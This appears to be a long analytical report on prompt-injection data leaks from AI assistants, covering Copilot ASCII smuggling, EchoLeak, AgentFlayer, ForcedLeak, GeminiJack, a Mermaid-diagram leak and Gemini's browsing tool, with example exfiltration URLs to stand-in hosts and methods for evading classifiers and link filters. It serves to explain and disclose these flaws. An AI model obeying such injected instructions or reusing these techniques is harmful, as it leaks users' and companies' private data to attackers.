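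The problem spread as people began talking to agents through messaging apps. In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reported that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Users could turn off link previews with one line in OpenClaw's settings. PromptArmor also ran a public test where people could check their own combinations of agent and app. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio agents among the affected platforms.

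Slack's developer guide, *Unfurling links in messages*, now advises developers to consider disabling link previews for messages written by a language model because of the risk of exfiltration, but previews remain on by default. PromptArmor wants chat apps to offer preview settings for individual chats or channels, so that a company could keep previews in conversations between colleagues and turn them off wherever an agent posts.

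### Copilot hides an email in a link

In the Slack AI attack, the victim had to ask about the secret. Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot removed that requirement because the injected instructions could make Copilot search for the secret.

Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes the attack. The attacker puts instructions for Copilot in an email to the victim or in a document shared with them. When the victim asks Copilot about the email or document, Copilot reads the instructions and searches the victim's mailbox for another message the attacker has described. Copilot ran this search without asking for approval. In the demonstrations, Rehberger used the attack to obtain sales figures and confirmation codes for signing in to Slack.

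This greatly increased what an attacker could reach with one malicious email. A request to summarise a harmless-looking document could now bring an unrelated email of the attacker's choice into the context. Rehberger added that the instructions could be set to take effect only when a particular person used Copilot on the item.

Rehberger then needed a way to get the email's text out of Copilot. Microsoft had fixed the image leak in Bing Chat the year before, so he had Copilot write a link containing the stolen text in characters the victim couldn't see.

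Computers store each character as a number assigned by the Unicode standard. One little-used part of Unicode, the Tags block, contains a second copy of the basic English letters, digits and punctuation marks. For instance, a capital H is number 48 in the hexadecimal notation programmers use, and its copy is number E0048. Virtually no font has shapes for these copies, according to *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (2026), so they take up no visible space on most screens. A language model processes the stored characters whether or not they are visible, and several leading models can read the copies as ordinary text and follow instructions written in them.

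Rehberger calls the technique ASCII smuggling, after the old standard for those basic characters. The malicious email included a worked example of the encoding, which helped Copilot apply it correctly. Copilot then produced a link that looked like a short, harmless address but also contained the text of the stolen email in invisible characters. If the victim clicked the link, all of that text went to the attacker's server, where the attacker could convert it back into readable letters.

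The link was better disguised than the one in the Slack attack, where hovering displayed the key in plain letters, but hovering could still reveal that something was odd about the address. The same invisible characters can also hide instructions in the malicious email, so an employee who reads it finds nothing suspicious. Embrace The Red noted in 2025 that Anthropic's models also followed such instructions, and that Anthropic did not consider this a security vulnerability.

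The victim of the Copilot attack had to use Copilot on the malicious item and click the link. Rehberger pointed out that Copilot might also retrieve the item by itself while answering another question, in which case the victim would only have to click the link.

### From "low severity" to a fix

Rehberger first reported the invisible characters to Microsoft on 17 January 2024, but his report did not include a complete attack. Microsoft closed it the next day as low severity. Rehberger objected that the severity would be higher if the technique were part of a longer attack, and got no reply.

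On 10 February, Rehberger submitted a new report showing the whole sequence and the theft of sales data. Microsoft opened a case three days later. In April it asked for time until the end of May, and Rehberger agreed to leave the attack out of a conference talk. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By 2 July Rehberger's demonstrations had stopped working, and on 22 August Microsoft raised no objection to publication. The Hacker News' *Microsoft Fixes ASCII Smuggling Flaw* (2024) also described the flaw as patched.

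Microsoft's first rating is understandable if one considers only the invisible characters, which don't move data anywhere. Slack judged searching public channels in a similar way, as OpenAI had judged displaying images in 2023. Each company assessed a feature that was harmless by itself but dangerous when combined with text from an attacker. Microsoft had less excuse than the others because, by January 2024, it had already fixed a leak in Bing Chat that combined injected instructions with an ordinary display feature.

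Rehberger had recommended that Copilot stop displaying the invisible characters, stop running searches automatically, and ideally stop displaying clickable links. Microsoft did not answer a question about which changes it had made. Rehberger observed that Copilot no longer seemed to turn addresses into clickable links, which would be enough on its own to stop this attack. But without clickable links, Copilot can't conveniently send employees to useful websites, so Microsoft had a reason to bring links back in some form.

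After the fix, a malicious email could still take control of Copilot's answer, and an attacker needed only a different way to get the data out. Another researcher, Michael Bargury, had demonstrated data theft from Copilot that August at the DEF CON security conference. Willison's *Links and materials for Living off Microsoft Copilot* describes a video in which the attack begins when a user asks for a summary of an email containing hidden text. By the time of the EchoLeak attack in 2025, Copilot was removing external links from its answers, according to *EchoLeak* (2025), and the attack sent the data out through an image.

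## EchoLeak: data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot by one email

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, the research department of the security startup Aim Security, reported an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that Aim named EchoLeak. The attacker sent an employee one email. If the employee later asked Copilot about a subject the email covered, displaying Copilot's answer sent data to the attacker's server. Rehberger's 2024 attack on Copilot had worked only if the victim used Copilot on a malicious email and then clicked a link, but EchoLeak needed neither step. Microsoft finished fixing it in May, and both companies made it public on 11 June 2025 as CVE-2025-32711.

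Microsoft had three defences that could have kept the email from sending data to the attacker's server: a filter on incoming text, a filter on links in Copilot's answers, and a Content Security Policy. Aim Labs got past all three. The main source on its method is a report by Itay Ravia of Aim Labs, which most later accounts rely on.

Suppose an employee has been discussing a planned takeover with Copilot, including the price the company means to offer, 6,150,000. The employee then asks how to apply for parental leave. Copilot searches for documents about leave and finds the company's policy, along with an email from a stranger that has a passage on the same subject.

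### An email written to its human reader

Microsoft screens text before it reaches Copilot's language model, using classifiers trained on examples to tell hostile text from harmless text. It calls them XPIA classifiers, after "cross-prompt injection attack", its term for indirect prompt injection. Such classifiers can recognise crude injected commands that address the assistant and tell it to ignore its instructions.

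Aim's email was worded as instructions to the person who received it, and it never mentioned Copilot or AI. The classifier let it through, and once the email was in the model's context, the model followed the instructions anyway.

Ravia considers such an email inherently difficult, but not impossible, to detect. Office mail is full of requests to collect information and put it somewhere, so a filter strict enough to stop every such attack would also block a good deal of legitimate work. Training a better classifier requires many examples of real injections, but Ravia notes that good collections are scarce, and an attacker can choose any topic, tone or language. A similar disguise had been used in the 2023 attack on Google's Bard, when Embrace The Red presented the instructions in the shared document as a demand from the legal department to everyone reading it.

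The email also told its "recipient" never to mention it, supposedly for compliance reasons. Copilot normally cites its sources, but it followed this instruction too and left the email out, so the employee would have had little reason to look for it. Aim could deliberately cause the kind of omission that PromptArmor had seen in Slack AI, where it apparently happened by chance.

### Two ways to write a link

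The researchers first planned to have Copilot show the employee a link with the stolen data in its address, much as in the Slack AI attack. Copilot had a defence against this, which removed markdown links to outside websites from its answers.

Markdown, however, has more than one notation for a link. In the common one, the address follows directly after the words that the reader sees:

`[leave policy](https://policy.example)`

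In the other, known as a reference-style link, the visible words are followed by a label, and the address stands on a line of its own:

```
[leave policy][1]

[1]: https://policy.example
```

Writers use reference-style links to keep long addresses out of their paragraphs. On screen, these look identical to ordinary links. Microsoft's filter recognised only ordinary links, so a reference-style link to an outside server stayed in Copilot's answer. Willison credits Microsoft with restricting ordinary links to approved internal destinations, but notes that it forgot to cover the lesser-known format.

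The gap arose because the filter detected only one link notation, while the program that displayed the chat window accepted several. This difference would not have mattered if Microsoft had checked the links after the chat window converted them to HTML, because the different notations become the same HTML.

Aim now had a working one-click attack. Markdown images use the same two notations as links, with an exclamation mark in front, and the filter had the same gap for them. A browser requests an image without a click, so Aim switched from links to images. Only the Content Security Policy still prevented the leak.

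### SharePoint, Teams and the list of trusted servers

Bing Chat's policy in 2023 allowed images from four domains. The list that Ravia reproduces for Microsoft 365 Copilot has 29 different entries, 11 of which cover every address under a domain. The list includes SharePoint, Teams, Bing, a LinkedIn picture server and various servers that host icons. The browser would have blocked an image from pictures.example, but the attacker could now make it request any address the list allowed, and needed only one server on the list that would pass the data on.

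Some of the usual tricks did not work. Ravia explains that the browser was expecting an image, so it would not follow a redirect to another site or run a script on the page it received. The forwarding therefore had to happen on Microsoft's side.

The researchers began with SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal company websites. Any subscriber, including an attacker, gets an address under sharepoint.com. Bard's policy had the same weakness, but Microsoft had already closed the closest equivalent to Google's public scripts. SharePoint no longer let customers add their own server-side code to a site or pass the extra information in a web address to an automated workflow. After what Ravia calls tedious digging, the team found a SharePoint function that fetches material from another website so that a page can embed it. If the request named the attacker's server and included the stolen data,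 SharePoint would send the data to that server.

That attack chain was complete, but it required the victim to connect to the attacker's SharePoint site and accept an invitation to view it. It would have worked on some employees, even though they had never heard of the site.

Teams, Microsoft's workplace chat program, had no such condition. One of its servers would fetch the content of any address given to it, a service that *EchoLeak*, the academic case study by Reddy and Gujral, identifies as part of the preview system. In the invented case, Copilot's answer about parental leave would end with an image whose address has roughly this form:

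`https://teams.example/fetch?url=pictures.example/6150000`

The browser allows the request because it goes to Teams. The Teams server then requests the second address, and 6150000 appears in the attacker's log.

This is a proxy fetch, like the one Slack makes to build a link preview. Willison described the Teams address as an open redirect, which sends the browser on to another site. By Ravia's account, the server made the second request itself. The difference is important because the browser would not have followed a redirect. It also affects what an investigator could find. Reddy and Gujral write that the request might reach the attacker from Microsoft's servers or from the victim's own internet address. If Ravia's description is right, it came from Microsoft, and a company examining its own network traffic would have seen an employee's computer making a routine connection to Teams.

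### Getting the email retrieved

The attack works only if Copilot retrieves the attacker's email from a mailbox that might hold tens of thousands of others. Press accounts were not always clear about this step. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, describes Copilot as scanning the user's mail in the background and acting on what it reads. SecurityWeek's *‘EchoLeak’ AI Attack Enabled Theft of Sensitive Data via Microsoft 365 Copilot* explains that the attack starts when the victim asks about something the email mentions, which agrees with Ravia's report. After sending the email, the attacker has to wait for such a question.

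Ravia found that an attacker who studies the company and guesses what its staff will ask still has a fairly poor chance of getting the email retrieved. Ravia assumed, without being certain, that Copilot searches by meaning, which would explain this. In such a search, an encoder turns each passage into numbers that work like a position on a map with many dimensions. A short email occupies one position, so the search finds it only when a question lands nearby.

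Copilot is more likely to retrieve the attacker's text if it covers many subjects, a technique Aim called "RAG spraying". The attacker can send many emails on different subjects or one very long email that covers many. Aim chose the long email, which works because retrieval systems usually split long documents into passages and encode each passage separately.

It also looked into a subtler way of spreading the passages out. A language model can usually interpret text with odd characters added or some letters replaced by symbols, but Ravia suspected that these changes would affect an encoder more. If so, an attacker could write the instructions once and garble them in a hundred different ways. The resulting passages would lie far apart on the map but mean the same thing to the model.

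To test this, the team used text-embedding-ada-002, a public encoder from OpenAI, and measured the cosine similarity between a text and its garbled copy. For two lists of numbers *a* and *b*, this is

cos(*a*, *b*) = (*a* · *b*) / (|*a*| |*b*|)

The top of the fraction multiplies each number in one list by its counterpart in the other and adds up the results. The bottom treats each list as an arrow and multiplies the two arrows' lengths. For (3, 4) and (4, 3), the top is 12 + 12 = 24 and both arrows have length 5, so the similarity is 24/25, or 0.96. Arrows pointing the same way score 1, and arrows at right angles score 0.

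Some garbled copies scored as low as 0.7 against their originals. Although the scale runs down to 0, this is a low score for the encoder, which gave a higher one to two unrelated subjects, "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science".

Aim nevertheless left the method out of EchoLeak. Microsoft doesn't publish which encoder Copilot uses, and copies that are well spread under one encoder may be bunched together under another, so the researchers couldn't tell which copies would be well spread under Copilot's. Ravia also reports similarity scores but no trial in which a model followed the garbled instructions, and 0.7 was the lowest score, not a typical one.

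The method they did use was much simpler. The email consisted of sections, each presented as a complete guide to a routine topic such as employee onboarding, common HR questions or leave of absence. Every section contained the same instructions. Employees at nearly every company ask about these topics, so the attacker needed to know nothing about the target except an email address.

According to Ravia, this was enough to make Copilot retrieve the email for questions on various topics. The report gives no success rate, which probably varied between companies. The attacker's passage would have had more competition for a place in the context at a firm with dozens of its own documents about leave than at a firm with none.

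### What the attacker could have reached

Aim Security's *EchoLeak M365 Copilot Vulnerability* states that the attack could leak any data in the model's context, including the whole chat history and whatever Copilot had fetched from the company's records. Cybersecurity Dive reported the same day that the data at risk was potentially everything Copilot had access to. That is a much larger amount, because the context for one answer holds only the conversation so far and a small selection of the documents an employee can open.

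In the invented case, the attacker got the takeover price because the employee had been discussing it in the same conversation. If the employee had opened a new chat and asked only about parental leave, the context would have contained the leave policy, the attacker's email, the names of the employee and the company, and perhaps a few other documents that matched the question. The attacker's instructions were to choose the most sensitive item in the context, but there might have been nothing worth stealing.

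In Rehberger's 2024 attack, the email made Copilot run a new search. The published EchoLeak chain has no such step, although several descriptions read as though it could do this too. Goldman's article describes Copilot digging into internal files, and Reddy and Gujral write that the email could coerce Copilot into accessing them. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) says that the chain made the assistant retrieve data beyond the malicious email, which is accurate if it refers to the documents Copilot fetched for the employee's own question. Given the 2024 attack, it is reasonable to suspect that an attacker could have combined EchoLeak with searches of their own choosing, but Aim's report doesn't demonstrate this.

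Aim showed that a stranger's email could make Copilot pick a secret from its context and send it out without the user clicking anything. The larger claim, that all of a company's Microsoft 365 data was at risk, requires further assumptions. One of these, that the same email could work repeatedly, is quite plausible. The email stayed in the mailbox, so Copilot could presumably retrieve it again the next time the user asked about leave or personnel matters, and each conversation would have exposed different data. Over some months, an attacker who emailed many employees might have collected a lot, though with little control over what came in.

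Aim's two accounts also differ on whether customers could have prevented the attack. Ravia's report, as it now appears on Cato Networks' website, says that to the best of Aim's knowledge, no administrator setting would have helped. Aim's earlier question-and-answer page says that Copilot's default settings had probably left organisations exposed, and that customers can make Copilot ignore outside emails or can protect documents with data loss prevention labels. Adir Gruss, Aim's co-founder and chief technology officer, also blamed the default configuration when speaking to Cybersecurity Dive.

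The timing may explain the conflict. Reddy and Gujral mention reports that Microsoft's patches introduced options to restrict Copilot's use of outside communications. If the option arrived only with the fix, both statements could be correct, the first in the months before the fix and the second on the day of publication. An assistant that ignored all outside mail would have been safe from this email, but with the drawback described earlier for employees who deal with customers. Labels would have protected only labelled documents.

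### "LLM scope violation" and the confused deputy

Aim thought that "indirect prompt injection" was too broad a category to help people design defences, and proposed a narrower one. Ravia compares this to buffer overflows, an old class of flaws in which a program writes more data into a piece of memory than will fit. Programmers named one type the stack overflow, and Ravia says this precise name was important in developing a precise protection, the "stack canary". The canary is a known value placed in memory so that the program can detect when something has overwritten it.

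The new term, "LLM scope violation", describes cases where instructions from an untrusted source make a model attend to trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. In EchoLeak, the sign of this was the email's request for the most sensitive information in the surrounding material. Ravia argues that an email from outside the company should not be able to refer to data from inside it.

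Ravia explains this through a feature of Unix, the family of operating systems that includes Linux. A program marked "suid" runs with the permissions of its owner rather than those of the person running it. The command for changing a password works this way so that an ordinary user can change one line in a protected file without having access to the rest. If the program doesn't properly limit what it does on request, an unprivileged user can misuse its permissions. In this comparison, the email corresponds to the unprivileged user, and the language model to the privileged program being misused.

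Security researchers have called this the "confused deputy" problem since the 1980s. Hardy's 1988 article *The Confused Deputy* tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine code, and choose a file for its debugging output. The compiler had permission to write to the system directory where it was installed, because it kept usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. One customer chose the billing file for the debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the records.

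The compiler used a permission that the operators had granted for one purpose to carry out a request from a customer who had no right to touch that file. Similarly, Copilot had the employee's permission to read the company's data and used that permission to follow the instructions in the email. Ravia's suid comparison describes a confused deputy without using the term.

Hardy's article offered a remedy called a capability, a token that both identifies a file and conveys the right to use it. If customers had to give the compiler a capability instead of a file name, they could direct it to the billing records only if they already had the right to change them. This works because the compiler can track which token came with which request, but a language model can't reliably attach different rights to different sentences in its context. In the NCSC's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, David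 C therefore proposes treating a model as an "inherently confusable deputy". As The Record, a cybersecurity news site, summarised it, the traditional fixes for confused deputies don't carry over to language models.

The official record, reproduced in GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), describes EchoLeak as "AI command injection" and lists it under injection flaws, the class that includes SQL injection. David C's post argues against this older view.

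Willison thought the pattern was old and needed no new term, and that it arose because a model cannot take account of where its text came from. "Scope violation" adds very little to "confused deputy" as an explanation of what went wrong. The idea of defining the problem by levels of trust is also older. Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, formally defined programs that are free of such attacks and worked out how that definition relates to information-flow integrity, the principle that untrusted input should not influence trusted data or decisions.

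The term may be more useful to someone building a filter. It draws attention to the email's request for information from outside itself, which the XPIA classifier apparently did not catch. A check for such requests could act before any data had left. Aim was selling a product based on this approach, which doesn't make the approach wrong but helps explain the wish for a distinct name.

Legitimate emails can also have this feature. A supplier may write, "Please check this invoice against the prices in our contract", and the employee who asks Copilot to deal with the invoice will want it to open the contract. The definition relies on "explicit consent" to handle such cases, but an employee who types "what should I do about this?" has neither given nor withheld it, so a filter's decision would be a guess.

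### Was it the first zero-click attack?

Ravia's report calls EchoLeak "the first known zero-click AI vulnerability". It later narrows this claim to the first zero-click flaw in a widely used generative AI product to have an AI weakness at its core, not rely on specific user behaviour and not restrict which data could be stolen. Aim argues that in earlier attacks, either the user had explicitly referred the chatbot to a malicious item or the attacker could take only a very limited kind of data.

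The earlier cases support most of this:

| Case | How the attacker's text reached the model | How the data left |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, spring 2023 | The user pasted copied text, or had a plugin read a web page | Image, no click |
| Bing Chat, 2023 | The user opened a web page and chatted about it | Image, no click |
| Bard, 2023 | The user brought a shared document into the chat | Image, no click |
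| NotebookLM, reported 2023 | The user uploaded a file | Image, no click |
| Slack AI, 2024 | The assistant retrieved a message by itself | Link, one click |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2024 | The user asked about an email or document | Link, one click |
| EchoLeak, 2025 | The assistant retrieved an email by itself | Image, no click |

The technique for sending data out without a click was two years old by then. Embrace The Red had described the image in the Bard attack as "zero click", and in April 2024 it wrote of a "zero-click image rendering scenario" in NotebookLM. Slack AI had also retrieved hostile text on its own in 2024, although that attacker needed an account in the company's workspace.

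EchoLeak combined the two halves and let a complete outsider start the attack, which none of the earlier cases in the table did. So under the stricter definition of zero-click, these cases don't contradict Aim's careful version of the claim.

In June 2025, Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* quoted Aim's report as calling EchoLeak "a novel practical attack" on an application built on a language model. The version of the report on Cato's website calls it "the first practical attack", but sales figures had been stolen from the same product a year earlier.

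Reddy and Gujral go further, describing EchoLeak as the first known case of someone weaponising prompt injection to take data from a production AI system. They write that such attacks were until then "largely considered theoretical", with no confirmed breaches in the real world. But the products on Rehberger's 2024 list of image leaks, which also includes Anthropic's Claude, were already in public use when the flaws became known. If only a confirmed breach of a real victim counts, EchoLeak doesn't qualify either, because it was a demonstration by researchers and Microsoft reported no affected customers.

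### The fix, and what it left in place

Gruss told Goldman that Aim had spent about three months studying how Copilot worked internally before it found the flaw. After the January report, Microsoft reserved a CVE number on 9 April and attempted a first fix that month. In May it found more security problems related to the flaw, and it completed the fix by the end of that month. Aim withheld its findings until then.

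Gruss put the total at five months, which he considered very long for a flaw of this kind. He attributed the delay partly to novelty, since Microsoft had to find the right teams and teach them about the problem. Microsoft's security staff had told Aim that the work was "super groundbreaking for them". The novelty explanation is only partly convincing, because Microsoft had dealt with Rehberger's similar attack on the same assistant the year before, and that repair had also taken nearly five months.

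Customers had nothing to install, since Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers. Microsoft said it had updated its products and was adding further defences, but did not specify which steps of the chain it had blocked. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. That would remove ready-made links from an incoming email, but a model can also compose a link from a description, so Microsoft presumably corrected the filter on Copilot's answers too.

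The case study appeared in November 2025 in the symposium proceedings of the Association for the Advancement of Artificial Intelligence. It relies on published accounts and was written without access to Copilot's internal workings. It states more explicitly than Aim did that the attacker has no account in the company, cannot question Copilot directly, and can only send text to an employee who uses Copilot now and then. It also matches each step of the attack to standard lists of security flaws and controls, which helps a company that has to show an auditor where such an attack fits.

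The paper's most ambitious addition is a grid that rates eight defences against six elements of the attack. According to the grid, clearly separating outside text from inside text stops the scope violation and the classifier bypass but not the automatic leak. A strict Content Security Policy stops the image, the proxy fetch and the leak but does nothing about the injection. Requiring human approval before Copilot uses outside content is rated as stopping the most elements, five of the six.

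The text beside the grid says that a tick means full coverage "in our tests", but the paper's limitations section says that no experiments were run, and the caption calls the grid theoretical. The grid is best read as a set of informed expectations, and one of them looks too optimistic. For a strict policy, the paper recommends allowing only the addresses that the application needs from the vendor's own domains. But Teams is on one of Microsoft's own domains, so a shorter list would have helped only if Microsoft had left off the server that made the proxy fetches, or had stopped that server from contacting addresses chosen by strangers. The paper also recommends restricting such proxies, which was the more important part of its advice for EchoLeak.

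Closing the Teams route also did not block the other servers on the list, including Bing's, which an attack on Copilot used in the same way the following year.

The repair also did not change how Copilot combines a stranger's email with a company's own documents. Gruss said the basic design flaw was that agents handle trusted and untrusted data in the same "thought process". He thought a lasting solution would need either a new design or compulsory controls around every agent. Aim had delayed publication partly in the hope that other vendors with similar products "will wake up". Gruss named Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, among the products that might have the same weakness.

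## 2025: the same leak in ChatGPT, Gemini and Salesforce assistants

In June 2025, the month EchoLeak became public, researchers privately reported similar leaks to Google and OpenAI. Salesforce received a report in July. By January 2026, security firms had published attacks on ChatGPT, several of Google's Gemini products and Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents. Another researcher had found a new way to get mail out of Microsoft 365 Copilot.

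As before, an outsider's text entered the context and the model followed the instructions in it. The attacks differ more in how the data got out. In some, the victim's browser sent it by loading an image or following a link (a browser-side exit). In others, the assistant requested the attacker's address using a browsing tool that runs on the vendor's computers (a server-side exit), so the data didn't pass through the victim's browser or the employer's network.

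### AgentFlayer: a picture in a trusted storage service

By the summer of 2025, ChatGPT had a feature called Connectors, which let it search a user's Google Drive, SharePoint, GitHub and other accounts. Employees could now ask it about company files, as they could with Copilot, and an attacker could try to steal data from those files as well as the chat transcripts targeted in 2023.

In August, the security firm Zenity published *AgentFlayer*, an attack on this feature. A user uploads a document to ChatGPT and asks for a summary. White text one pixel high in the document instructs the model to search the user's Google Drive for API keys instead, and to display an image whose URL contains the keys. The hidden text also includes a story about a developer with a deadline, because ChatGPT otherwise tended to refuse to handle secrets.

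The first attempt failed because OpenAI's address check, in use since December 2023, rejected Zenity's test server. The researchers then put an ordinary picture in Azure Blob Storage, where customers of Microsoft's cloud keep files, and the check accepted its address. With an invented key and a placeholder domain, the address looked roughly like this:

`https://storage.example/photo.png?key=CURLEW-5518`

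The key doesn't change the picture that the storage service returns. But Azure customers can log every request for their files, including the part of the URL after the question mark, so the attacker could read the key in the log. The check had treated the service as safe, although anyone can rent space on it.

Others besides Zenity found such gaps. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes the same use of Azure storage to send out a user's recent conversations. Tenable found that the check always accepted links under bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that forward the browser to the listed site, so anyone with a site in Bing's index already had an approved link to it.

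Zenity's "0-click" attack does not meet the strict definition when the victim has to upload the malicious document. Michael Bargury, who had demonstrated data theft from Copilot the year before, also described a version that comes closer. The attacker shares the document with the victim, and it appears in the victim's Google Drive disguised as a company policy on meetings. Bruce Schneier's *We Are Still Unable to Secure LLMs from Malicious Inputs* (2025) quotes an account of the demonstration video, in which the victim asks ChatGPT to summarise a recent meeting. The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data* reports that receiving the shared document was enough to expose a user. This omits the victim's request to ChatGPT, although asking about a meeting is ordinary use.

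Zenity was also worried about insiders. A dishonest employee could hide instructions in every document they had access to and wait for a colleague to use ChatGPT on one of them.

Zenity's report mentions no repair of the Azure route, but OpenAI substantially revised its address check around the same month. The current rule might allow the picture's plain address, but it would block the one ending in CURLEW-5518 because that address would never have been public.

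### ForcedLeak: a trusted domain for five dollars

Companies that use Salesforce to keep track of customers can put its Web-to-Lead form on their websites. A visitor enters a name, a company and a question, and the entry goes straight into the sales database as a "lead", or possible customer. Anyone on the internet can therefore use the form to put text where Agentforce, Salesforce's AI assistant, will read it, without knowing an employee's email address.

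Noma Labs, Noma Security's research team, tested what a hostile visitor could do with the form. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces Noma's report on a security forum. The name, company and email fields hold 40 or 80 characters each, too few for elaborate instructions, but the description field holds 42,000. Noma filled it with numbered questions. In the test, an employee asked Agentforce to look up the lead by name, answer the person's questions and draft a reply. Sales assistants get requests like this all the time, and answering the questions more or less means treating the description as a list of tasks.

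One item on the list was a request for the email addresses of the company's other leads, and another was a request for an image with those addresses in its URL. Noma had earlier asked the agent what colour red and yellow make. It answered "Orange", which suggested that it wasn't restricted to sales matters.

Salesforce had a Content Security Policy (CSP) to stop the browser from loading the picture. The policy allowed 22 domains or groups of domains, most of them belonging to Salesforce or Slack. Salesforce had let the registration of one domain lapse, so anyone could buy it, and Noma did for $5. A CSP contains only domain names, not their owners, so the browser still treated the domain as allowed and sent the data to Noma's server.

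Salesforce had let its allowed domain expire, whereas in the 2023 attack on Bard, Google still owned the allowed domain but let strangers run scripts on it. The expired domain may not have been the only way to send data out, because the same policy allowed every address under amazonaws.com, where anyone can rent storage and log requests, much as Zenity did with Azure. Noma does not report testing this. Willison, in *ForcedLeak*, called the flaw a classic "lethal trifecta" image leak.

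Noma reported the attack on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce had fixed the flaw by 8 September. Salesforce regained control of the expired domain and began enforcing a rule called Trusted URLs. A spokesperson told Martin (2025, *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed*) that the patches stop agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. Customers' administrators decide which outside domains to trust. They have to add every domain their agents need or risk disruption, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*.

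A separate list of domains for each customer is a much tighter limit than one long list for everybody, but each customer now has to notice if a supplier on its list stops paying for a domain name. According to Salesforce's *Security Advisories*, Salesforce also began requiring a person's confirmation that August for some standard Agentforce actions, such as cancelling an order or resetting a password. This makes an injected instruction less dangerous in general, but it would not have stopped ForcedLeak, because displaying a picture is not one of those actions.

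After those repairs, the firm Capsule Security found another way to get company data out of Agentforce through a public form, according to the OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce* (2026), an April entry in its monitor of AI incidents. Salesforce patched that flaw too.

### GeminiJack: one search that starts another

Gemini Enterprise is Google's assistant for organisations. An administrator chooses which sources it may search, such as Gmail, Calendar and Docs, and employees can then search all of them with one question. Noma found a leak in it and told Google on 5 June 2025, six days before EchoLeak became public.

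The attacker shares a Google Doc with an employee or sends them a calendar invitation or an email. *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration* (Paganini, 2025) quotes Noma's description of the next steps. The employee searches for something routine, such as "Q4 Budget plans", and the retrieval system brings the attacker's document into the context along with the genuine ones. Instructions in the document make Gemini search all the connected sources for a word like "acquisition" and put the results in the address of an image. The employee's browser then requests that image from the attacker's server.

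As Aim published it, EchoLeak could steal only data that the employee's conversation and question had brought into the assistant's context. GeminiJack let the attacker choose what to search for. Rehberger's 2024 attack on Copilot had also allowed this, but GeminiJack didn't require the victim to ask about the malicious item or click a link. An employee's search for budgets could therefore leak emails about a takeover.

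Paganini also repeats the claim that one injection could take years of email, a full calendar and entire document stores. The assistant could search all of that, but it could not have leaked a company's archive in one answer, because the model has to write out the stolen text and a single image address can hold only a modest amount. The attacker's document would have stayed in place, however, so the assistant could have sent more each time a new search retrieved it. In a later leak from the email app Superhuman, which Willison described in January 2026, one malicious email made the assistant send out content from dozens of others, including financial, legal and medical messages, when the user asked for a summary of recent mail.

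Google took about five months to fix GeminiJack. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data*, the company confirmed in August that it had received the vulnerability report. It then changed how Gemini Enterprise and Vertex AI Search, a related tool for building search services, work with the systems that retrieve and index documents, and completely separated the two products. Noma published its findings on 8 December.

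Noma says in its report that Google's fix "addresses the core issue of instruction/content confusion" in the retrieval process. But Sasi Levi, Noma's head of security research, told SC Media for *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* that Google had not disclosed the technical details, and that Noma did not know whether Google had cleaned the incoming content, changed how the software reads it or rebuilt the retrieval system. Without those details, it is hard to accept that Google solved the core issue, which nobody else is known to have solved. It is safer to conclude only that Noma's attack no longer works.

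### A login button in a Copilot diagram

Microsoft 365 Copilot can draw diagrams using Mermaid, a tool that turns a few lines of text into a picture of boxes and arrows. In October 2025 the researcher Adam Logue published an attack that used this feature to get around Copilot's restrictions on links.

The attack began when a user asked Copilot to summarise an Excel file. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, white text spread over several sheets gradually diverted Copilot from the summary to another task. Copilot fetched the user's recent emails, encoded them and drew a diagram that looked like a login button. A summary of Logue's post on daily.dev explains that the button was a link with the encoded emails in its address, so clicking it to "log in" sent them to the attacker. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration*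 (2025) contrasts this one-click attack with a similar flaw in the programming tool Cursor that needed no click.

EchoLeak got past Microsoft's filter by using a lesser-known markdown notation for links. Mermaid has its own link notation, so even a complete filter for markdown links could miss a link in a Mermaid diagram. Every feature that turns the model's text into something clickable needs its own protection, unless a single check runs after all of them have finished.

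Logue reported the flaw on 15 August and Microsoft fixed it on 26 September. Copilot can still draw diagrams, but users can no longer click on anything in them. This blocks one route for leaking data and inconveniences few people, since few need a clickable diagram. The fix only affects how data gets out, so hidden text in a spreadsheet could presumably still spoil a summary.

### Gemini's browsing tool as the way out

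By the spring of 2025, Google had restricted the familiar exits in its main Gemini assistant. Tenable's *The Trifecta* (2025) notes that Gemini no longer displayed outside images, that it sent links through a google.com address and cut off suspicious output, and that it sometimes refused to answer when it detected an injection. (Gemini Enterprise evidently lacked the restriction on images, or GeminiJack would not have worked that June. Google had likewise repaired the image leak one product at a time in 2023 and 2024.)

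Tenable looked for a feature that could send data without displaying anything, and found it in the tool that Gemini uses to read web pages. Suppose Gemini uses this tool to summarise a page whose address contains the user's name and city. The tool has to request the page first, and the request sends the name and city to whoever runs the site. Gemini's answer needs no image or link, so rules about images and links don't prevent the leak.

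A plain instruction to send the user's details to a website failed because Gemini detected that the request was unusual. The researchers then read Gemini's "Show thinking" display, which revealed how the model called its browsing tool. When they wrote the instruction in the same form, Gemini carried it out.

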